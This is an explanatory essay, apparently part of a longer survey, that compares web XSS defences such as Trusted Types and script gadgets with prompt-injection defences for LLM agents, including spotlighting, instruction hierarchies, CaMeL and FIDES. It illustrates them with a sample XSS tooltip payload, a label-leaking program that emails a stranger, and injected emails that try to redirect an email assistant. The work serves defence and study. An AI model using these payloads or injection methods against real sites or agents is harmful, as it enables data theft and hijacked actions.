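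This is good evidence that nonces are easier to maintain, but weaker evidence of how many attacks they stop. Fewer than 1% of the script policies surveyed used nonces, so the survey couldn't compare the two approaches on equal terms. Based on hundreds of past bugs at Google, where they all worked, the researchers expected nonces to stop a large majority of XSS.

A separate study, *Complex Security Policy* by Roth, Barron and colleagues, traced the history of policies on 10,000 popular sites and found that even lists that seemed secure could fail because they named an expired or misspelled domain, which an attacker could register. In 2025, Chrome's engineers began a trial of a setting that lets developers permit individual script addresses instead of trusting whole sites, according to The Chromium Projects' *Quarterly Updates* (2026). Mozilla's *Goodbye innerHTML, Hello setHTML* (2026) concludes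 that too few websites adopted CSP to protect most of the web, because it requires large changes to existing sites and continual review by experts.

### Values that only approved code can make

Even a good policy has trouble with DOM-based XSS, because a script the company trusts may pass a stranger's text to a function like `eval`. Google's engineers proposed Trusted Types, which changes what these functions accept. The W3C draft standard, *Trusted Types* (2024), describes the accepted values as "non-spoofable, typed values in place of strings".

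With the feature switched on, the webmail company could write:

```
const mailPolicy = trustedTypes.createPolicy("mail", {
  createHTML: (text) => sanitize(text),
});

heading.innerHTML = term;                         // error
heading.innerHTML = mailPolicy.createHTML(term);  // accepted
```

The first assignment fails because `term` is an ordinary string. In the second, the policy passes the string through a sanitizer, which removes dangerous HTML, and the browser wraps the result in a `TrustedHTML` object. Other code can't forge this object, and holding it gives code the right to insert that particular piece of HTML, so it works a little like an object capability.

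A `TrustedHTML` object is a very coarse record of origin. It shows that an approved policy produced the HTML, but not who wrote the original text. The browser needs only the first fact to decide whether to accept the HTML.

About 60 browser functions can turn text into code. Trusted Types lets a reviewer concentrate on the policies instead of checking every use of those functions. Michał Bentkowski, who had earlier broken Caja with escaped variable names, said in The Daily Swig's *Google checks rise of DOM XSS with Trusted Types* that "it makes the process a whole lot easier."

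Google had already enforced the same idea in its compilers, which check and prepare code before release. The compilers reject direct use of the dangerous functions and require values of special types instead. Developers can make such a value from text written in the program itself, which an attacker can't change, or by using a sanitizer or a strict template. If none of these is flexible enough, they can ask a security expert to approve a conversion that accepts any string.

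Wang and colleagues report that one large product had ten DOM-based XSS bugs in the year before it adopted these rules, two during the year of adoption and one the year after. This was a single product with no comparison group, and its team was among the most committed. But across Google, DOM-based XSS made up a shrinking share of serious reported bugs, and a growing proportion of the remaining cases came from old code that didn't follow the rules, which suggests that the rules helped. They were also practical. By the end of 2020, the company had exempted fewer than 1% of its more than one million JavaScript files, and in the early months reviewers received fewer than eight requests a week.

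### Results at Google and support in browsers

Google then turned on Trusted Types in the browser. *Trusted Types* (Kotowicz, 2021) reported that more than 130 Google services enforced it and that nobody had found DOM-based XSS in them since they began doing so. *A Deep Dive into JS Trusted Types Violations* (2025) reports the same for Gmail and AppSheet, a tool for building apps, in the year after they adopted Trusted Types. By August 2025, Google (2025) was preparing a talk on how it had introduced nonces and Trusted Types across hundreds of products.

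These results are impressive, but they count only the bugs that people found, and they come from the company that designed the feature. Many of the services had also already adopted nonce-based policies and Google's special types. Kotowicz's more cautious estimate is that Trusted Types would have prevented at least 61% of the DOM-based XSS bugs that outsiders had reported to Google. The others involved faulty sanitizers, the AngularJS framework, or "legacy conversions", exemptions for old code that nobody has rewritten yet.

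Outside Google, Microsoft's code editor Visual Studio Code has enforced Trusted Types since January 2021. An automatic check of its nearly one million lines found 108 places that needed changes, three quarters of which were trivial to fix and needed no policy. Some programs need no policies at all. The developers of Chromium's built-in pages could forbid policies, which leaves no approved way to turn a string into code.

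Chrome and other browsers built on Chromium added this protection in 2020 and for years were the only ones to offer it. Mozilla engineers worried that it was too complex for ordinary websites, but Mozilla changed its position in December 2023. Frédéric Wang's *Intent to ship* (2025) reported that Safari had added support in version 26 and that Firefox would follow in version 148. All major browser engines have supported Trusted Types since that Firefox release in February 2026, according to web.dev's *February 2026 Baseline monthly digest* (2026).

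### Policies that approve anything

The browser checks that a policy made the value, not that the policy did anything useful. This one turns off the protection:

`createHTML: (text) => text`

Any script can define a policy unless the website restricts which policies are allowed. When Kotowicz wrote, Google's services didn't use that restriction, so a newly added package could have created a careless policy. Google relied on checking the source code to prevent this.

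In *Trust Me If You Can*, Roth, Gröber and colleagues tested how well developers write policies. They asked 13 people with web development experience to add Trusted Types to a small application that included content from Twitter and Facebook and an advertising widget. Only seven produced a secure policy for HTML. Every HTML sanitizer that participants wrote from scratch was easy to bypass. Some removed `<script` but left the `onerror` code on images, which is enough for the search-page attack.

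Several participants also used an HTML sanitizer on JavaScript, which replaced the less-than sign in `i <= 5` with `&lt;` and broke the advertisement. Escaping that is correct for one language can be wrong for another, a problem that contextual templates solve automatically. Ten of the 13 participants liked Trusted Types less after trying it. The sample is small, and the advertising widget's use of `eval` made the task difficult, but many real websites depend on outside code that also uses `eval`.

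Most websites are therefore better off with an existing sanitizer. When Google archived Caja, it recommended the sanitizer in Closure Library, its collection of JavaScript code. Google retired that library too, on 1 August 2024. The maintainers wrote on the library's page that it no longer met the needs of modern JavaScript development and told users to look for alternatives, without naming any.

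No single product has replaced it. For Trusted Types, Google had released a smaller library, safevalues, in 2021, which helps developers create approved values. DOMPurify, an independent sanitizer, was the one that successful participants in the study used. Browsers are also beginning to do the job themselves. Firefox 148 introduced `setHTML`, which a developer can use in place of `innerHTML`:

`heading.setHTML(term);`

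`setHTML` sanitizes text as it inserts it. By default, it removes the image in the search example along with its code. Mozilla points out that a strict Trusted Types policy can allow `setHTML` and block the unsafe ways of inserting HTML. Developers who do this no longer have to write or choose an HTML sanitizer. A built-in sanitizer should also avoid the kind of mistake behind Caja's 2019 breach, when Caja and the browser interpreted the same HTML differently.

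### Script gadgets

An attacker may not need to inject code if a trusted script will turn harmless-looking text into code. *Code-Reuse Attacks for the Web* (Lekies, Kotowicz and colleagues, 2017) calls pieces of trusted code that do this "script gadgets".

Suppose the webmail page has a script that finds every element with a `data-tip` attribute and displays its contents as a tooltip:

```
tip.innerHTML = element.getAttribute("data-tip");
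```

An attacker sends an email containing this HTML:

`<b data-tip="&lt;img src=x onerror=deleteInbox()&gt;">Hello</b>`

A sanitizer that permits such attributes, as DOMPurify did by default, finds only bold text with a note in an attribute. But the browser converts `&lt;` back to `<` when it reads the attribute, and the company's own script then inserts the result as HTML. If nothing else blocks it, the image's code runs.

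Lekies and colleagues looked for gadgets in 16 popular JavaScript libraries and frameworks. They found ways past DOMPurify in nine of them, past Closure's sanitizer in six, and past nonce-based policies in only four. Adding `strict-dynamic`, which made nonces practical for large sites, raised that last number to 13. Many libraries create new scripts from text they find in the page, and `strict-dynamic` makes the browser trust those scripts.

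The researchers then crawled the 5,000 most popular websites. They confirmed working gadgets on 19.88% of the 4,557 domains left after merging duplicates and dropping sites that didn't respond. They simulated the initial injection and didn't adapt the attacks to each site's defences, so they couldn't necessarily have broken into a fifth of the sites. But their program didn't log in or click on anything, so it probably missed many gadgets.

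Trusted Types stops the tooltip attack because the script tries to assign an ordinary string to `innerHTML`. It offers less protection against frameworks with their own small programming languages. Aurelia, for example, looks for expressions in the page's HTML and evaluates them itself. An attacker could inject an expression that started from a page element and followed its `ownerDocument` property to the whole page, the same route guests had used to escape ADsafe. The browser runs only Aurelia's trusted code, which looks up each property named in the attacker's text, and never parses the expression as JavaScript. Kotowicz advised developers to abandon AngularJS, which has a similar design, because Trusted Types couldn't make it secure.

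### Why escaping works

Escaping is reliable because the browser's HTML parser follows exact, published rules. The characters `&lt;` display a less-than sign and can never begin a tag, whatever text follows them. A template system can apply the same rules in advance to determine where each inserted value will land and which characters would let it break out. Escaping didn't help in Aurelia's case because a second interpreter, with different rules, read the text after the browser had parsed it.

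The rules determine only what counts as code. The stranger's email giving a false address for Bob contains nothing to escape, so the webmail page would display it as written. A language model has no parser that enforces such rules, whatever marks a developer puts around the text.

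## Marking untrusted text inside a model's input

A developer can still mark untrusted text and instruct the model to treat it differently, and the model's maker can train it to do so. Trusted and untrusted text stay in one input, so the agent works as before. The designs differ in what the mark is, who applies it, and what makes the model respond to it.

### Delimiters and spotlighting

The simplest marks are delimiters, characters that show where the untrusted text begins and ends. *Defending Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks With Spotlighting* (2024) gives the example of a summarization application whose code puts each document between double angle brackets. The system prompt, which holds the developer's standing instructions, tells the model never to obey instructions between those brackets. Spotlighting is the general name for this and similar ways of altering untrusted text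 so that the model can recognize it.

Suppose the developer of the email assistant uses the version in *RAISED* (2026). The system prompt now includes a warning that tool outputs appear between « and », and that the model must not follow instructions inside them. When the user asks the assistant to send the meeting notes to Bob, the model searches the inbox for Bob's address. Ordinary code wraps the search result in these marks and adds it to the model's input. The result includes the stranger's email, with its line about forwarding invoices.

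If the model follows the system prompt, it ignores that line, takes Bob's address from another email, and sends the notes. If it doesn't, it calls the email tool with the invoices attached, and the tool sends them because the marks have no effect outside the model.

The code should also remove any « or » from the emails, so that a stranger can't make the marked section seem to end early. This resembles escaping text for an HTML parser, though with a model it works usually rather than always.

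The marks don't help with the stranger's other email, which gives a false address for Bob, because the model is supposed to look for addresses in the marked text.

A variant called datamarking repeats the mark throughout the text. With a caret between words, that email would look like this:

`Hi,^Bob^here,^this^is^my^new^address.`

Google tested a similar defence for its Gemini models, inserting a mark every eight characters in an email's sender, subject and body. *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) concludes that it worked mainly by breaking up the tokens of phrases that would otherwise trigger the model. This fits poorly with the theory behind spotlighting, because the model may have been less likely to recognize an instruction, rather than more likely to ignore one because it came from an untrusted source.

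Developers can also repeat the user's task after every tool result, which is called prompt sandwiching. Like spotlighting, it needs no extra training, but it makes the input longer.

### Instruction hierarchies

With an instruction hierarchy, the marks are part of the model's input format. The provider's software labels each message as coming from the developer, the user or a tool. The labels use reserved tokens that ordinary text can't normally produce, so a stranger can't turn an email into a user request by typing a fake label.

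OpenAI proposed this method in 2024. It trained models to follow the higher-ranked source, using examples in which instructions from different sources conflicted. In the meeting notes example, the user's request outranks the stranger's line, which arrived in a tool result. Bob's real email has the same low rank, but the model can still take his address from it because the ranking applies only to instructions.

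Untrusted input can't forge a reserved label, just as untrusted JavaScript code can't forge an object reference. But a JavaScript engine prevents code from using an object without a reference to it, while labeling text "tool" only makes a model less likely to follow instructions in it.

### StruQ and SecAlign

StruQ, which researchers at the University of California, Berkeley, published in 2024, separates prompts from data, much as a database receives commands separately from values. The application supplies the trusted prompt and the data in two fields. A small program puts reserved tokens around each field and deletes any imitation of those tokens from the data. The researchers then fine-tuned (further trained) an existing model on examples where the data contained an extra instruction and the correct answer did not follow it.

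SecAlign keeps the two fields but changes the training. Each training example has a good answer, which follows only the prompt, and a bad answer, which follows the injected instruction. The model learns to prefer the good answer.

In both designs, a program separates the fields as strictly as a database interface does. But the model then reads both fields as one sequence of tokens, and only its training discourages it from obeying instructions in the second.

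### Fixed attacks and adaptive attacks

Researchers usually measure these defences by the attack success rate, the share of attempts that achieve the attacker's goal. *Evaluating Prompting-Based Defenses Against Domain-Camouflaged Injection Attacks* (Pai, 2026) reports 3,510 trials on three inexpensive models, using 45 tasks based on invented professional documents. When the attacks were blunt commands to ignore earlier instructions, spotlighting reduced their success rate from 38.9% to 11.1% on Gemini 2.0 Flash and from 21.1% to 15.6% on Llama 3.1 8B. Claude Haiku 4.5 resisted all of these blunt attacks without any defence.

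Spotlighting did much less against attacks that read like part of the document. Their success rate went from 21.1% to 20.0% on Gemini, from 22.2% to 23.3% on Llama, and from 14.4% to 6.7% on Haiku. Pai describes the Haiku result as a halving, but with 90 trials in each group, the drop from 13 successes to six could be chance.

Having another model rewrite each document in neutral language worked better, with attacks succeeding 3.3% to 10.0% of the time. This takes an extra model call for each document, and it would presumably preserve a false email address, since the rewrite changes the wording but keeps the factual claims.

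Pai's attacks didn't change in response to the defence. An adaptive attacker knows which defence is in place and keeps revising the attack until it works. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) collects results from several studies of such attackers.

StruQ and SecAlign both originally reported attack success rates near zero. Adaptive attacks succeeded about 100% of the time against StruQ on one benchmark and 80% to 100% of the time on another. Against SecAlign, they succeeded 88% and 46% of the time on the same two benchmarks. Even without adaptation, existing attacks succeeded 68% and 75% of the time on those benchmarks against the instruction hierarchy in GPT-4o-mini, an OpenAI model from 2024.

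The broadest comparison, by Nasr and colleagues, covered twelve published defences, most of which had also reported attack success rates near zero. Adaptive attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of them, including above 95% for spotlighting and sandwiching and 96% for Meta SecAlign, a later model trained in a similar way. Human attackers had a 100% success rate.

Some of these attackers could inspect the model's weights, the numbers it learned in training, which outsiders can't do with most commercial models. The models were also weaker than today's. But the results show that the original tests measured resistance only to a known list of attacks, and people had mistaken this for resistance to attackers, who can also try new ones.

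### Results for current models

Developers now use adaptive attacks in training. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026), its report on the model's safety tests, describes training the model against an automated attacker while preserving its ability to complete legitimate tasks. In OpenAI's internal tests, the share of indirect injection attacks the model resisted rose from 96.23% to 99.79%, making successful attacks about 18 times rarer. For direct injection, the model resisted 99.99% of attacks.

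Attacks through tools and outside content have tended to be harder to resist than direct ones, as TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) noted of an earlier OpenAI model. Robustness also varies within a family of models. *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense* (Cross, 2026) reports a score for another GPT-6 model that would mean it failed far more often than Astra.

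OpenAI's internal tests use the same automated approach as its training, so outside tests are better evidence. The security company Gray Swan tested Astra on 1,810 attacks selected from its 2026 competitions. It estimated that an attacker with 15 attempts at a scenario would succeed 8.5% of the time, down from 27.0% for GPT-5.6 Sol.

Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, has reported lower rates. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that Gray Swan's attack success rate against Claude Opus 5 was 2.0% after 15 attempts, and that no attack succeeded in 129 browser scenarios. The table compares these results with older ones from Anthropic's system cards, as reported by Narisetty and colleagues and by VentureBeat.

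| Model | Test | Attack success rate | Source |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | Coding, adaptive attacker | 4.7% after 1 attempt, 33.6% after 10, 63.0% after 100 | Narisetty and colleagues |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Graphical interface, no added safeguards | 17.8% after 1 attempt, 78.6% after 200 | VentureBeat |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | Gray Swan | 5.5% after 15 attempts | The Decoder |
| Claude Opus 5 | Gray Swan | 2.0% after 15 attempts | The Decoder |
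| GPT-5.6 Sol | Gray Swan | 27.0% after 15 attempts | OpenAI |
| GPT-6 Astra | Gray Swan | 8.5% after 15 attempts | OpenAI |

The first two rows come from different tests, so they can't be compared directly with the rest. The Gray Swan rows show rapid improvement at both companies, and both released even newer models in November 2026.

A score of zero also calls for caution. Opus 4.6 resisted all 200 attack attempts in a coding test in February 2026. In June, Digital Applied (2026) reported an attack success rate of 2.09% for its successor, Opus 4.8, in an adaptive coding test, and 0.41% for the newer Claude Fable 5. It seems more likely that the attacks had improved than that Opus 4.8 was less robust than Opus 4.6.

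*FrontierBreach*, a benchmark of office tasks from the AI security company PromptArmor, reports successful attacks on leading models from every provider. The models include Google's Gemini 4 Carbon, which PromptArmor says no other known benchmark had successfully attacked.

### The case for relying on the model

Marking and training preserve the flexibility that makes an agent useful. The assistant can read the whole inbox, find Bob's address wherever it is, and change its plan if Bob has asked for the notes in another format. No one has to decide beforehand which emails may influence which actions. Delimiters add only a few tokens to each tool result, and an application benefits from better training just by switching to a newer model.

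A well-trained model might also catch attacks that contain no instructions. For example, it could flag Bob's "new address" for the user to confirm because it came from an unfamiliar sender. Marks alone would never trigger that check, because they don't indicate whether an address is plausible. OpenAI trains Astra to follow a policy on when to request approval, such as before it sends certain messages.

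The improvement extends beyond the usual injection tests. OpenAI also gave its models a browsing task with a simulated message board that encouraged them to disclose private information or approve illicit access. GPT-5.6 Sol followed such instructions in 52% of runs, and Astra followed them in none.

### A low failure rate and a boundary

The usual reply is that an attacker can try again. If each attempt succeeds with probability *p*, independently of the others, the chance of at least one success in *n* attempts is

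`1 − (1 − p)ⁿ`

For Opus 4.5, *p* was 4.7%, so the formula predicts a 38% chance of success within ten attempts and 99% within 100. The measured figures were 33.6% and 63.0%, so a defence that stopped more than 95% of first attempts still failed in most scenarios within 100 attempts. Retrying helped less than the formula predicts, probably because the model was much harder to fool in some scenarios than in others.

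In practice, a stranger who sends an email may not learn whether the attack failed, and repeated attempts may attract attention. Extra safeguards also reduced the attacks' success rate after 200 attempts from 78.6% to 57.1% in the test of Opus 4.6 with a graphical interface.

But an attacker can target many people instead of retrying one. Astra's average failure rate in OpenAI's indirect tests was 0.21%. At that rate, if an email reached 100,000 assistants, about 210 of them would act on it. A real attacker would also send whichever attack worked best rather than an average one.

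A browser that enforces Trusted Types rejects an ordinary string no matter how many times an attacker tries it. The browser's code may have bugs, as Caja's did, but an attacker has to find one, and fixing it closes that route. An attacker may get past a model just by rewording the attack. Narisetty and colleagues argue that no amount of training can guarantee a refusal, and that this kind of defence "reduces incidents; it does not bound them". Defences outside the model have faced far fewer adaptive tests, so their results also need to be read with caution.

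In December 2025, *OpenAI says prompt injections that can trick AI browsers like ChatGPT Atlas* (Nolan, 2025) reported a similar concession from OpenAI, that such attacks might never be fully solved. Astra's results nine months later were far better but still included failures. A 2% risk may be acceptable if the worst outcome is a bad summary of a newsletter, but it is harder to accept when the assistant can send out a company's invoices, which nobody can take back.

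## CaMeL and its successors: separating the planner from the reader

Engineers who don't want to rely on a model to resist malicious instructions can assume that it will obey anything it reads and give it no power to misuse. In April 2023, the developer Simon Willison proposed the dual-model pattern, a simple way to do this that splits an agent into a planner and a reader. The planner decides which tools to call based on the user's request, and never sees untrusted text. The reader processes emails and other untrusted text but has no tools. Ordinary software stores the reader's answers in variables and shows the planner only their names, so the planner can order "send the notes to `$VAR1`" without seeing the address stored there.

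The stranger's line about forwarding invoices then reaches only the reader, which may follow it but can do nothing except return an odd answer. Willison (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, recommends assuming that anyone who gets text into a model's input controls everything that model does next. Under that assumption, the stranger controls the reader's answers but not the agent's choice of tools.

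The false address remains a problem because the reader might return it as Bob's. The reader's answer can also contain secrets. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) gives the example of a reader that sees private notes together with an incoming email. An injected line makes the reader quote the notes in its draft reply, and the agent sends the reply as planned.

### The meeting notes in CaMeL

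CaMeL, which Google DeepMind published in 2025, adds a check on what the agent does with the reader's answers. As Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, explain, the planner writes a program in a restricted form of Python, and an interpreter runs it. For the meeting notes, the program might look like this:

```
notes = find_document("today's meeting notes")
emails = search_inbox("Bob")
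address = ask_reader("Find Bob's address", emails, EmailAddress)
send_email(to=address, body=notes)
```

The planner writes all four lines before the agent opens any email. The interpreter then runs the two searches and stores the results in variables. On the third line, it gives the emails to the reader and requires the answer to be an email address.

The interpreter also attaches a capability tag to every value, which records where the value came from (Sources) and who may see it (Readers). The tag on `address` shows that the value came from the inbox by way of the reader. The tag on `notes` lists the people who have access to that document.

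Before the interpreter sends the email, it runs a tool-call policy, a Python function that looks at the arguments and their tags and either allows or denies the call. A simple policy could be:

```
def check_send_email(to, body):
    if is_trusted(to) or to in readers(body):
        return Allowed()
    return Denied("This person may not read the text.")
```

The first condition covers an address that the user typed. Bob's address came from an email, so the message can go only if his address meets the second condition. If the user has already shared the notes with Bob, his real address is on the list and he gets them. The stranger's address isn't on the list, so the policy blocks it. Both addresses came from the inbox, so the Sources tag can't distinguish them, but the Readers tag on the notes can.

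If the user has never shared the document with Bob, this policy also blocks his real address. Nikolaou and colleagues use a very similar program to demonstrate a stricter rule. It requires the recipient to come from a trusted source, and it always rejects the program. The agent would then have to ask the user for the address.

A stranger can still influence a program that contains a choice. If the planner writes "if Bob has replied, send the notes, otherwise send a reminder", a false email can decide which of the two happens, but it can't add a third possibility. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) calls this kind of influence branch steering.

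### Tags and object capabilities

A capability tag describes a value and has no effect unless a policy checks it, whereas an object capability gives its holder the right to do something. The tag is more like the browser's `TrustedHTML` type, which also records something about a value's history, though much less than a capability tag does.

The reader is the part of CaMeL that most resembles a guest in an object-capability system. It starts with no tools and receives only the text the planner's program passes it. Like the untrusted pocket calculator, the worst it can do is give a wrong answer. CaMeL combines both older remedies by limiting the reader's power and tracking where its answers go.

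### Why tools need declared return formats

CaMeL's planner has to write the whole program before any tool runs, so every tool needs a description of exactly what it returns. If the planner writes `emails[0].sender` but the field is named `from`, the program fails. An ordinary agent depends less on such descriptions because it can look at a tool's result before deciding what to do with it.

Many tools lack a return format. Peters-Gill and colleagues had to add one to every tool in the two benchmarks they used, and the original CaMeL evaluation needed the same change. They consider this a modest job that developers do once for each set of tools.

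A return format shows the planner that an email will have a sender and a body, but not what the body will contain. Suppose the task is to send Bob some notes, but he has written that he is on leave and that Carol needs them. An ordinary assistant might read this and ask the user what to do. CaMeL's program sends the notes to Bob unless the plan covers this case. Peters-Gill and colleagues found that most of CaMeL's failures on legitimate tasks came from committing to a plan before seeing the data. In other cases, one agent couldn't find data for the requested dates and returned data for nearby dates instead, which the waiting program used without detecting the difference.

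### Labels in an ordinary agent loop

Microsoft's FIDES lets the planner choose one tool call at a time, as most agents do. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025) describes how it tracks labels through this loop. Each piece of data has an integrity label, trusted or untrusted, and a confidentiality label, which in the simplest version is public or secret. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) gives the order of these labels as

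`trusted ⊑ untrusted` and `public ⊑ secret`

where data may flow only from left to right. When software combines two values, the result gets the label further to the right. A summary of one trusted and one untrusted document is therefore untrusted.

Applied directly, this rule would soon leave an agent unable to act, because once the planner had read one email, its whole conversation and every later tool call would be untrusted. FIDES avoids this by hiding untrusted results in variables, as the dual-model pattern does. The planner can query a separate reader about a hidden variable, and the reader's output must have a restricted form.

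The planner in FIDES receives each trusted result before it chooses the next step, so it doesn't have to plan the entire task in advance. FIDES still applies its policies when the planner calls a sensitive tool. According to Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026), the company added FIDES to its Agent Framework in May 2026, so developers can use it without building their own interpreter.

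### How a label can get lost

Labels protect data only if the software never loses one. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, found a way to make CaMeL lose one. The following program, based on their example, tells a stranger whether the user's bank balance is above a certain amount:

```
low = True
rich = True
if balance > limit: low = False
if low: rich = False
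if rich: send_email("stranger@example.com", "Rich!")
```

CaMeL would block a program that sent the email directly under the condition `balance > limit`, because that condition depends on a secret. But here, if the balance is above the limit, the third line changes `low` to false and the interpreter marks it as secret. The fourth line then does nothing, so `rich` stays true and still counts as public, and the email goes out. Otherwise, `rich` becomes false and no email goes out, so in both cases the stranger learns whether the balance is above the limit.

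An honest request doesn't require the planner to write this program, and a stranger's email can't cause it to, because the planner never reads the email. The flaw therefore weakens CaMeL's guarantee more than its everyday protection. Garby and colleagues also found a more ordinary bug. Inserting an untrusted value into a longer text, as planners often do, made the result count as trusted.

Another leak was in the code around the interpreter. When a program fails, CaMeL lets the planner try again, and the interpreter doesn't track this retry loop. A secret can determine whether a policy blocks an attempt, so each attempt can reveal one bit of the secret, and repeated attempts can reveal all of it.

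Garby and colleagues responded by designing LLMbda, a small programming language for agents that labels every value and every conversation with a model. They used the proof checker Lean to prove that secrets can't affect public results, except by determining whether a program finishes. Similarly, untrusted data can't affect trusted results unless the program uses the command `endorse` to relabel an untrusted value as trusted. A reviewer can find every such exception by searching for `endorse`.

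Their test agent, Randori, avoids the retry problem by first trying out its program in a simulated world. The planner can correct the program there as often as necessary, because all the data is artificial. Randori then runs the finished program on the real data.

### Letting only narrow answers through

Some tasks require the planner to learn something from untrusted text. An agent that repairs software, for instance, has to find out which bugs people have reported. In *Better Privilege Separation for Agents by Restricting Data Types*, Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues (2025) let the reader send the planner only values that can't contain an instruction: whole numbers, decimal numbers, true-or-false values and choices from a list that the developer wrote. The planner can then learn a bug's type and line number without seeing the reporter's words.

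One of their test agents shops online using customer reviews, any of which could contain an injection. Its reader scores each review on how strongly it supports the product and how relevant it is. The planner receives only the median of each score and the number of reviews, so a single malicious review has little influence. An attacker who wrote most of the reviews could still change the result.

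No attack succeeded against the shopping agent, a calendar agent or a bug-fixing agent with this design. The shopping and calendar agents remained as useful as before. A number or a category is often enough to choose a product, for example. The bug-fixing agent became less useful because a programmer usually wants to read the bug report.

*Towards Safe Autonomy for Computer Use* (2026) describes a related design that masks the parts of a web page that outsiders may have written. The site's owner marks those parts, or a model identifies them from the page's structure with the content removed. The agent can then query a reader about a masked part and may get back a number, a date, a true-or-false value or a choice from a list.

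A narrow answer can still be false. A malicious email might cause the reader to classify it as "urgent" instead of "general". Garby and colleagues limit the attacker's influence to at most log₂ *n* bits when the reader chooses from *n* categories, which is three bits for eight categories. The potential harm depends on what the agent does with the category.

Text is much harder to restrict. Strings could pass safely through Figma's membrane, but they are the most dangerous values to give a language model. Willison discusses a proposal to let a coding agent see function names of up to 30 characters from untrusted documentation. He doubts that this limit is short enough, since an attacker could name a function `run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance`, which refers to a command that deletes files.

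An email address is also free text, but CaMeL can handle one because the planner never sees it. In a design with narrow types, software could instead list the addresses in the user's contacts and let the reader choose one. The stranger's address wouldn't be on the list, though the reader might still choose the wrong Bob's address.

### How much protection the policies add

Garby and colleagues tested how much of CaMeL's security comes from separating the models and how much from its policies. They used the banking tasks in AgentDojo, a benchmark that gives agents simulated office work and plants injections in the data. They ran each of the 144 combinations of task and attack up to three times. In 97 of them, the attacker needed a tool call that wouldn't appear in a sensible plan for the task, such as a money transfer when the agent was only summarizing recent transactions. In the other 47,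 the plan already contained a step that the attacker could use.

When CaMeL ran on MiMo-v2.5 with the policies off, three of the 141 attacks in the second group succeeded. None succeeded with the policies on, but the number of tasks CaMeL completed when it wasn't under attack fell from 34 of 48 to 18. With GPT-5.2, no attack in the second group succeeded even with the policies off, and turning them on still reduced the number of completed tasks from 32 to 18.

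In this test, the policies prevented very few attacks and blocked almost half of the work that CaMeL could otherwise do. They may be more useful against an attacker who adapts to the design, because AgentDojo's attacks are fixed and mostly try to give the model new orders. The separation alone can't stop attacks that supply a false address or account number.

Randori completed 36 of the 48 tasks with GPT-5.2, even though its label checks were always on. Across three models, two of 1,296 attacks succeeded. Removing the `endorse` command reduced the number of completed tasks from 36 to 30 with one model and from 31 to 26 with another. There were only 16 different tasks, so small differences between the agents don't mean much, but the gap between Randori and CaMeL with its policies is large.

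### Results with small models and harder attacks

CaMeL also depends on the planner's ability to write a working program. *CapLite* (Xu, Liu and Nakayama, 2026) tested CaMeL on 15 models that anyone can download, most small enough to run on a personal computer. CaMeL let through 20 of 13,935 attacks, 17 of them on one model. Progent, a defence in which the model writes its own permission rules, let through 676, and 2,322 succeeded against agents with no defence.

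The small models were bad at writing CaMeL's programs. With one model, 68% of runs never produced a program the interpreter could execute. CaMeL allows up to ten rounds of repairs, which helps explain why it used 93,700 tokens per run. Without an attack, CaMeL completed 24.9% of tasks, compared with 59.4% for the undefended agents.

In CapLite, the researchers' own design, the planner writes a list of actions instead of a program. The list covers every action that will change something, and the planner writes it before the agent reads any data. It can contain gaps, such as an event's number, which a model later fills by choosing from values that ordinary software has extracted. The software then checks each action and accepts a recipient, an amount or a web address only if the user's request contains exactly that value.

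The request to send Bob the notes doesn't contain his address, so CapLite prompts the user to confirm the one it found. That prevents the stranger's attack as long as the user notices that the address is wrong.

None of the 13,935 attacks succeeded against CapLite. It used 17,100 tokens per run, and CaMeL used about 5.5 times as many. But CapLite wasn't much more useful. When there was no attack, it completed 28.1% of tasks. Every request for confirmation counted as a failure, but these were only about a tenth of the failures. More often, the small model had left a necessary action out of its list.

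CapLite needed both its fixed plan and its final check on recipients and other values. Xu and colleagues also tested it with parts removed, using eight of the models and 7,432 attacks. Without the check, 106 attacks succeeded. When they kept the check but let the planner add actions after reading the data, 53 succeeded.

In *The Devil is in the Context*, Chang, Nikolić and colleagues (2026) used a stronger model, GPT-5.6-Luna, and harder attacks. They began with 40 AgentDojo cases in which the model resisted every attack without help. Another model then rewrote the attacks so that each one stayed on the topic of the user's task, applied only under a stated condition, and changed the content of an action instead of adding a new one. One example is an instruction to report a lower total than the invoice shows.

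These attacks succeeded in 17.5% of the 40 cases without a defence and 2.5% with CaMeL, but CaMeL completed only 27.5% of the users' tasks. With a filter that used a language model to remove injected instructions, 7.5% of the attacks succeeded and the agent completed 90% of the tasks. The difference in successful attacks between CaMeL and the filter, one against three, could easily be chance, but the difference in completed tasks, 11 against 36, could not. Because the filter relies on a language model, it is still open to adaptive attacks.

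The drop in task completion that CaMeL causes should shrink as models improve. Peters-Gill and colleagues tested CaMeL with five models on AssetOpsBench, a set of industrial maintenance tasks, and found that it reduced the share of completed tasks by 21.6 percentage points on average. For the two strongest models, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5, the reduction was 13.4 points. They used no policies, so these figures don't include the kind of loss that Garby and colleagues measured. *ToolFence* (2026) reports that CaMeL was also significantly slower than defences that only filter text or add a warning to the prompt.

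### Checking a program before it runs

CaMeL checks each tool call only when the program reaches it, so an agent may do a lot of work before a policy stops it. Nikolaou and colleagues' CaMeLoT checks the planner's program in advance. It converts the program into a diagram of all the states it could pass through, then uses a standard verification tool to test rules such as:

`AG(call_send_direct_message ⇒ recipient_trusted)`

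`AG` means "in every state, on every possible path". If the program breaks the rule, the tool produces an example of how, and the planner uses it to write a better program.

CaMeLoT could express 22 of the 28 CaMeL policies in the comparison. The other six depend on facts known only when the program runs, such as who has access to a file. The policy that let Bob receive the notes depends on that kind of fact. CaMeLoT therefore leaves these checks to CaMeL.

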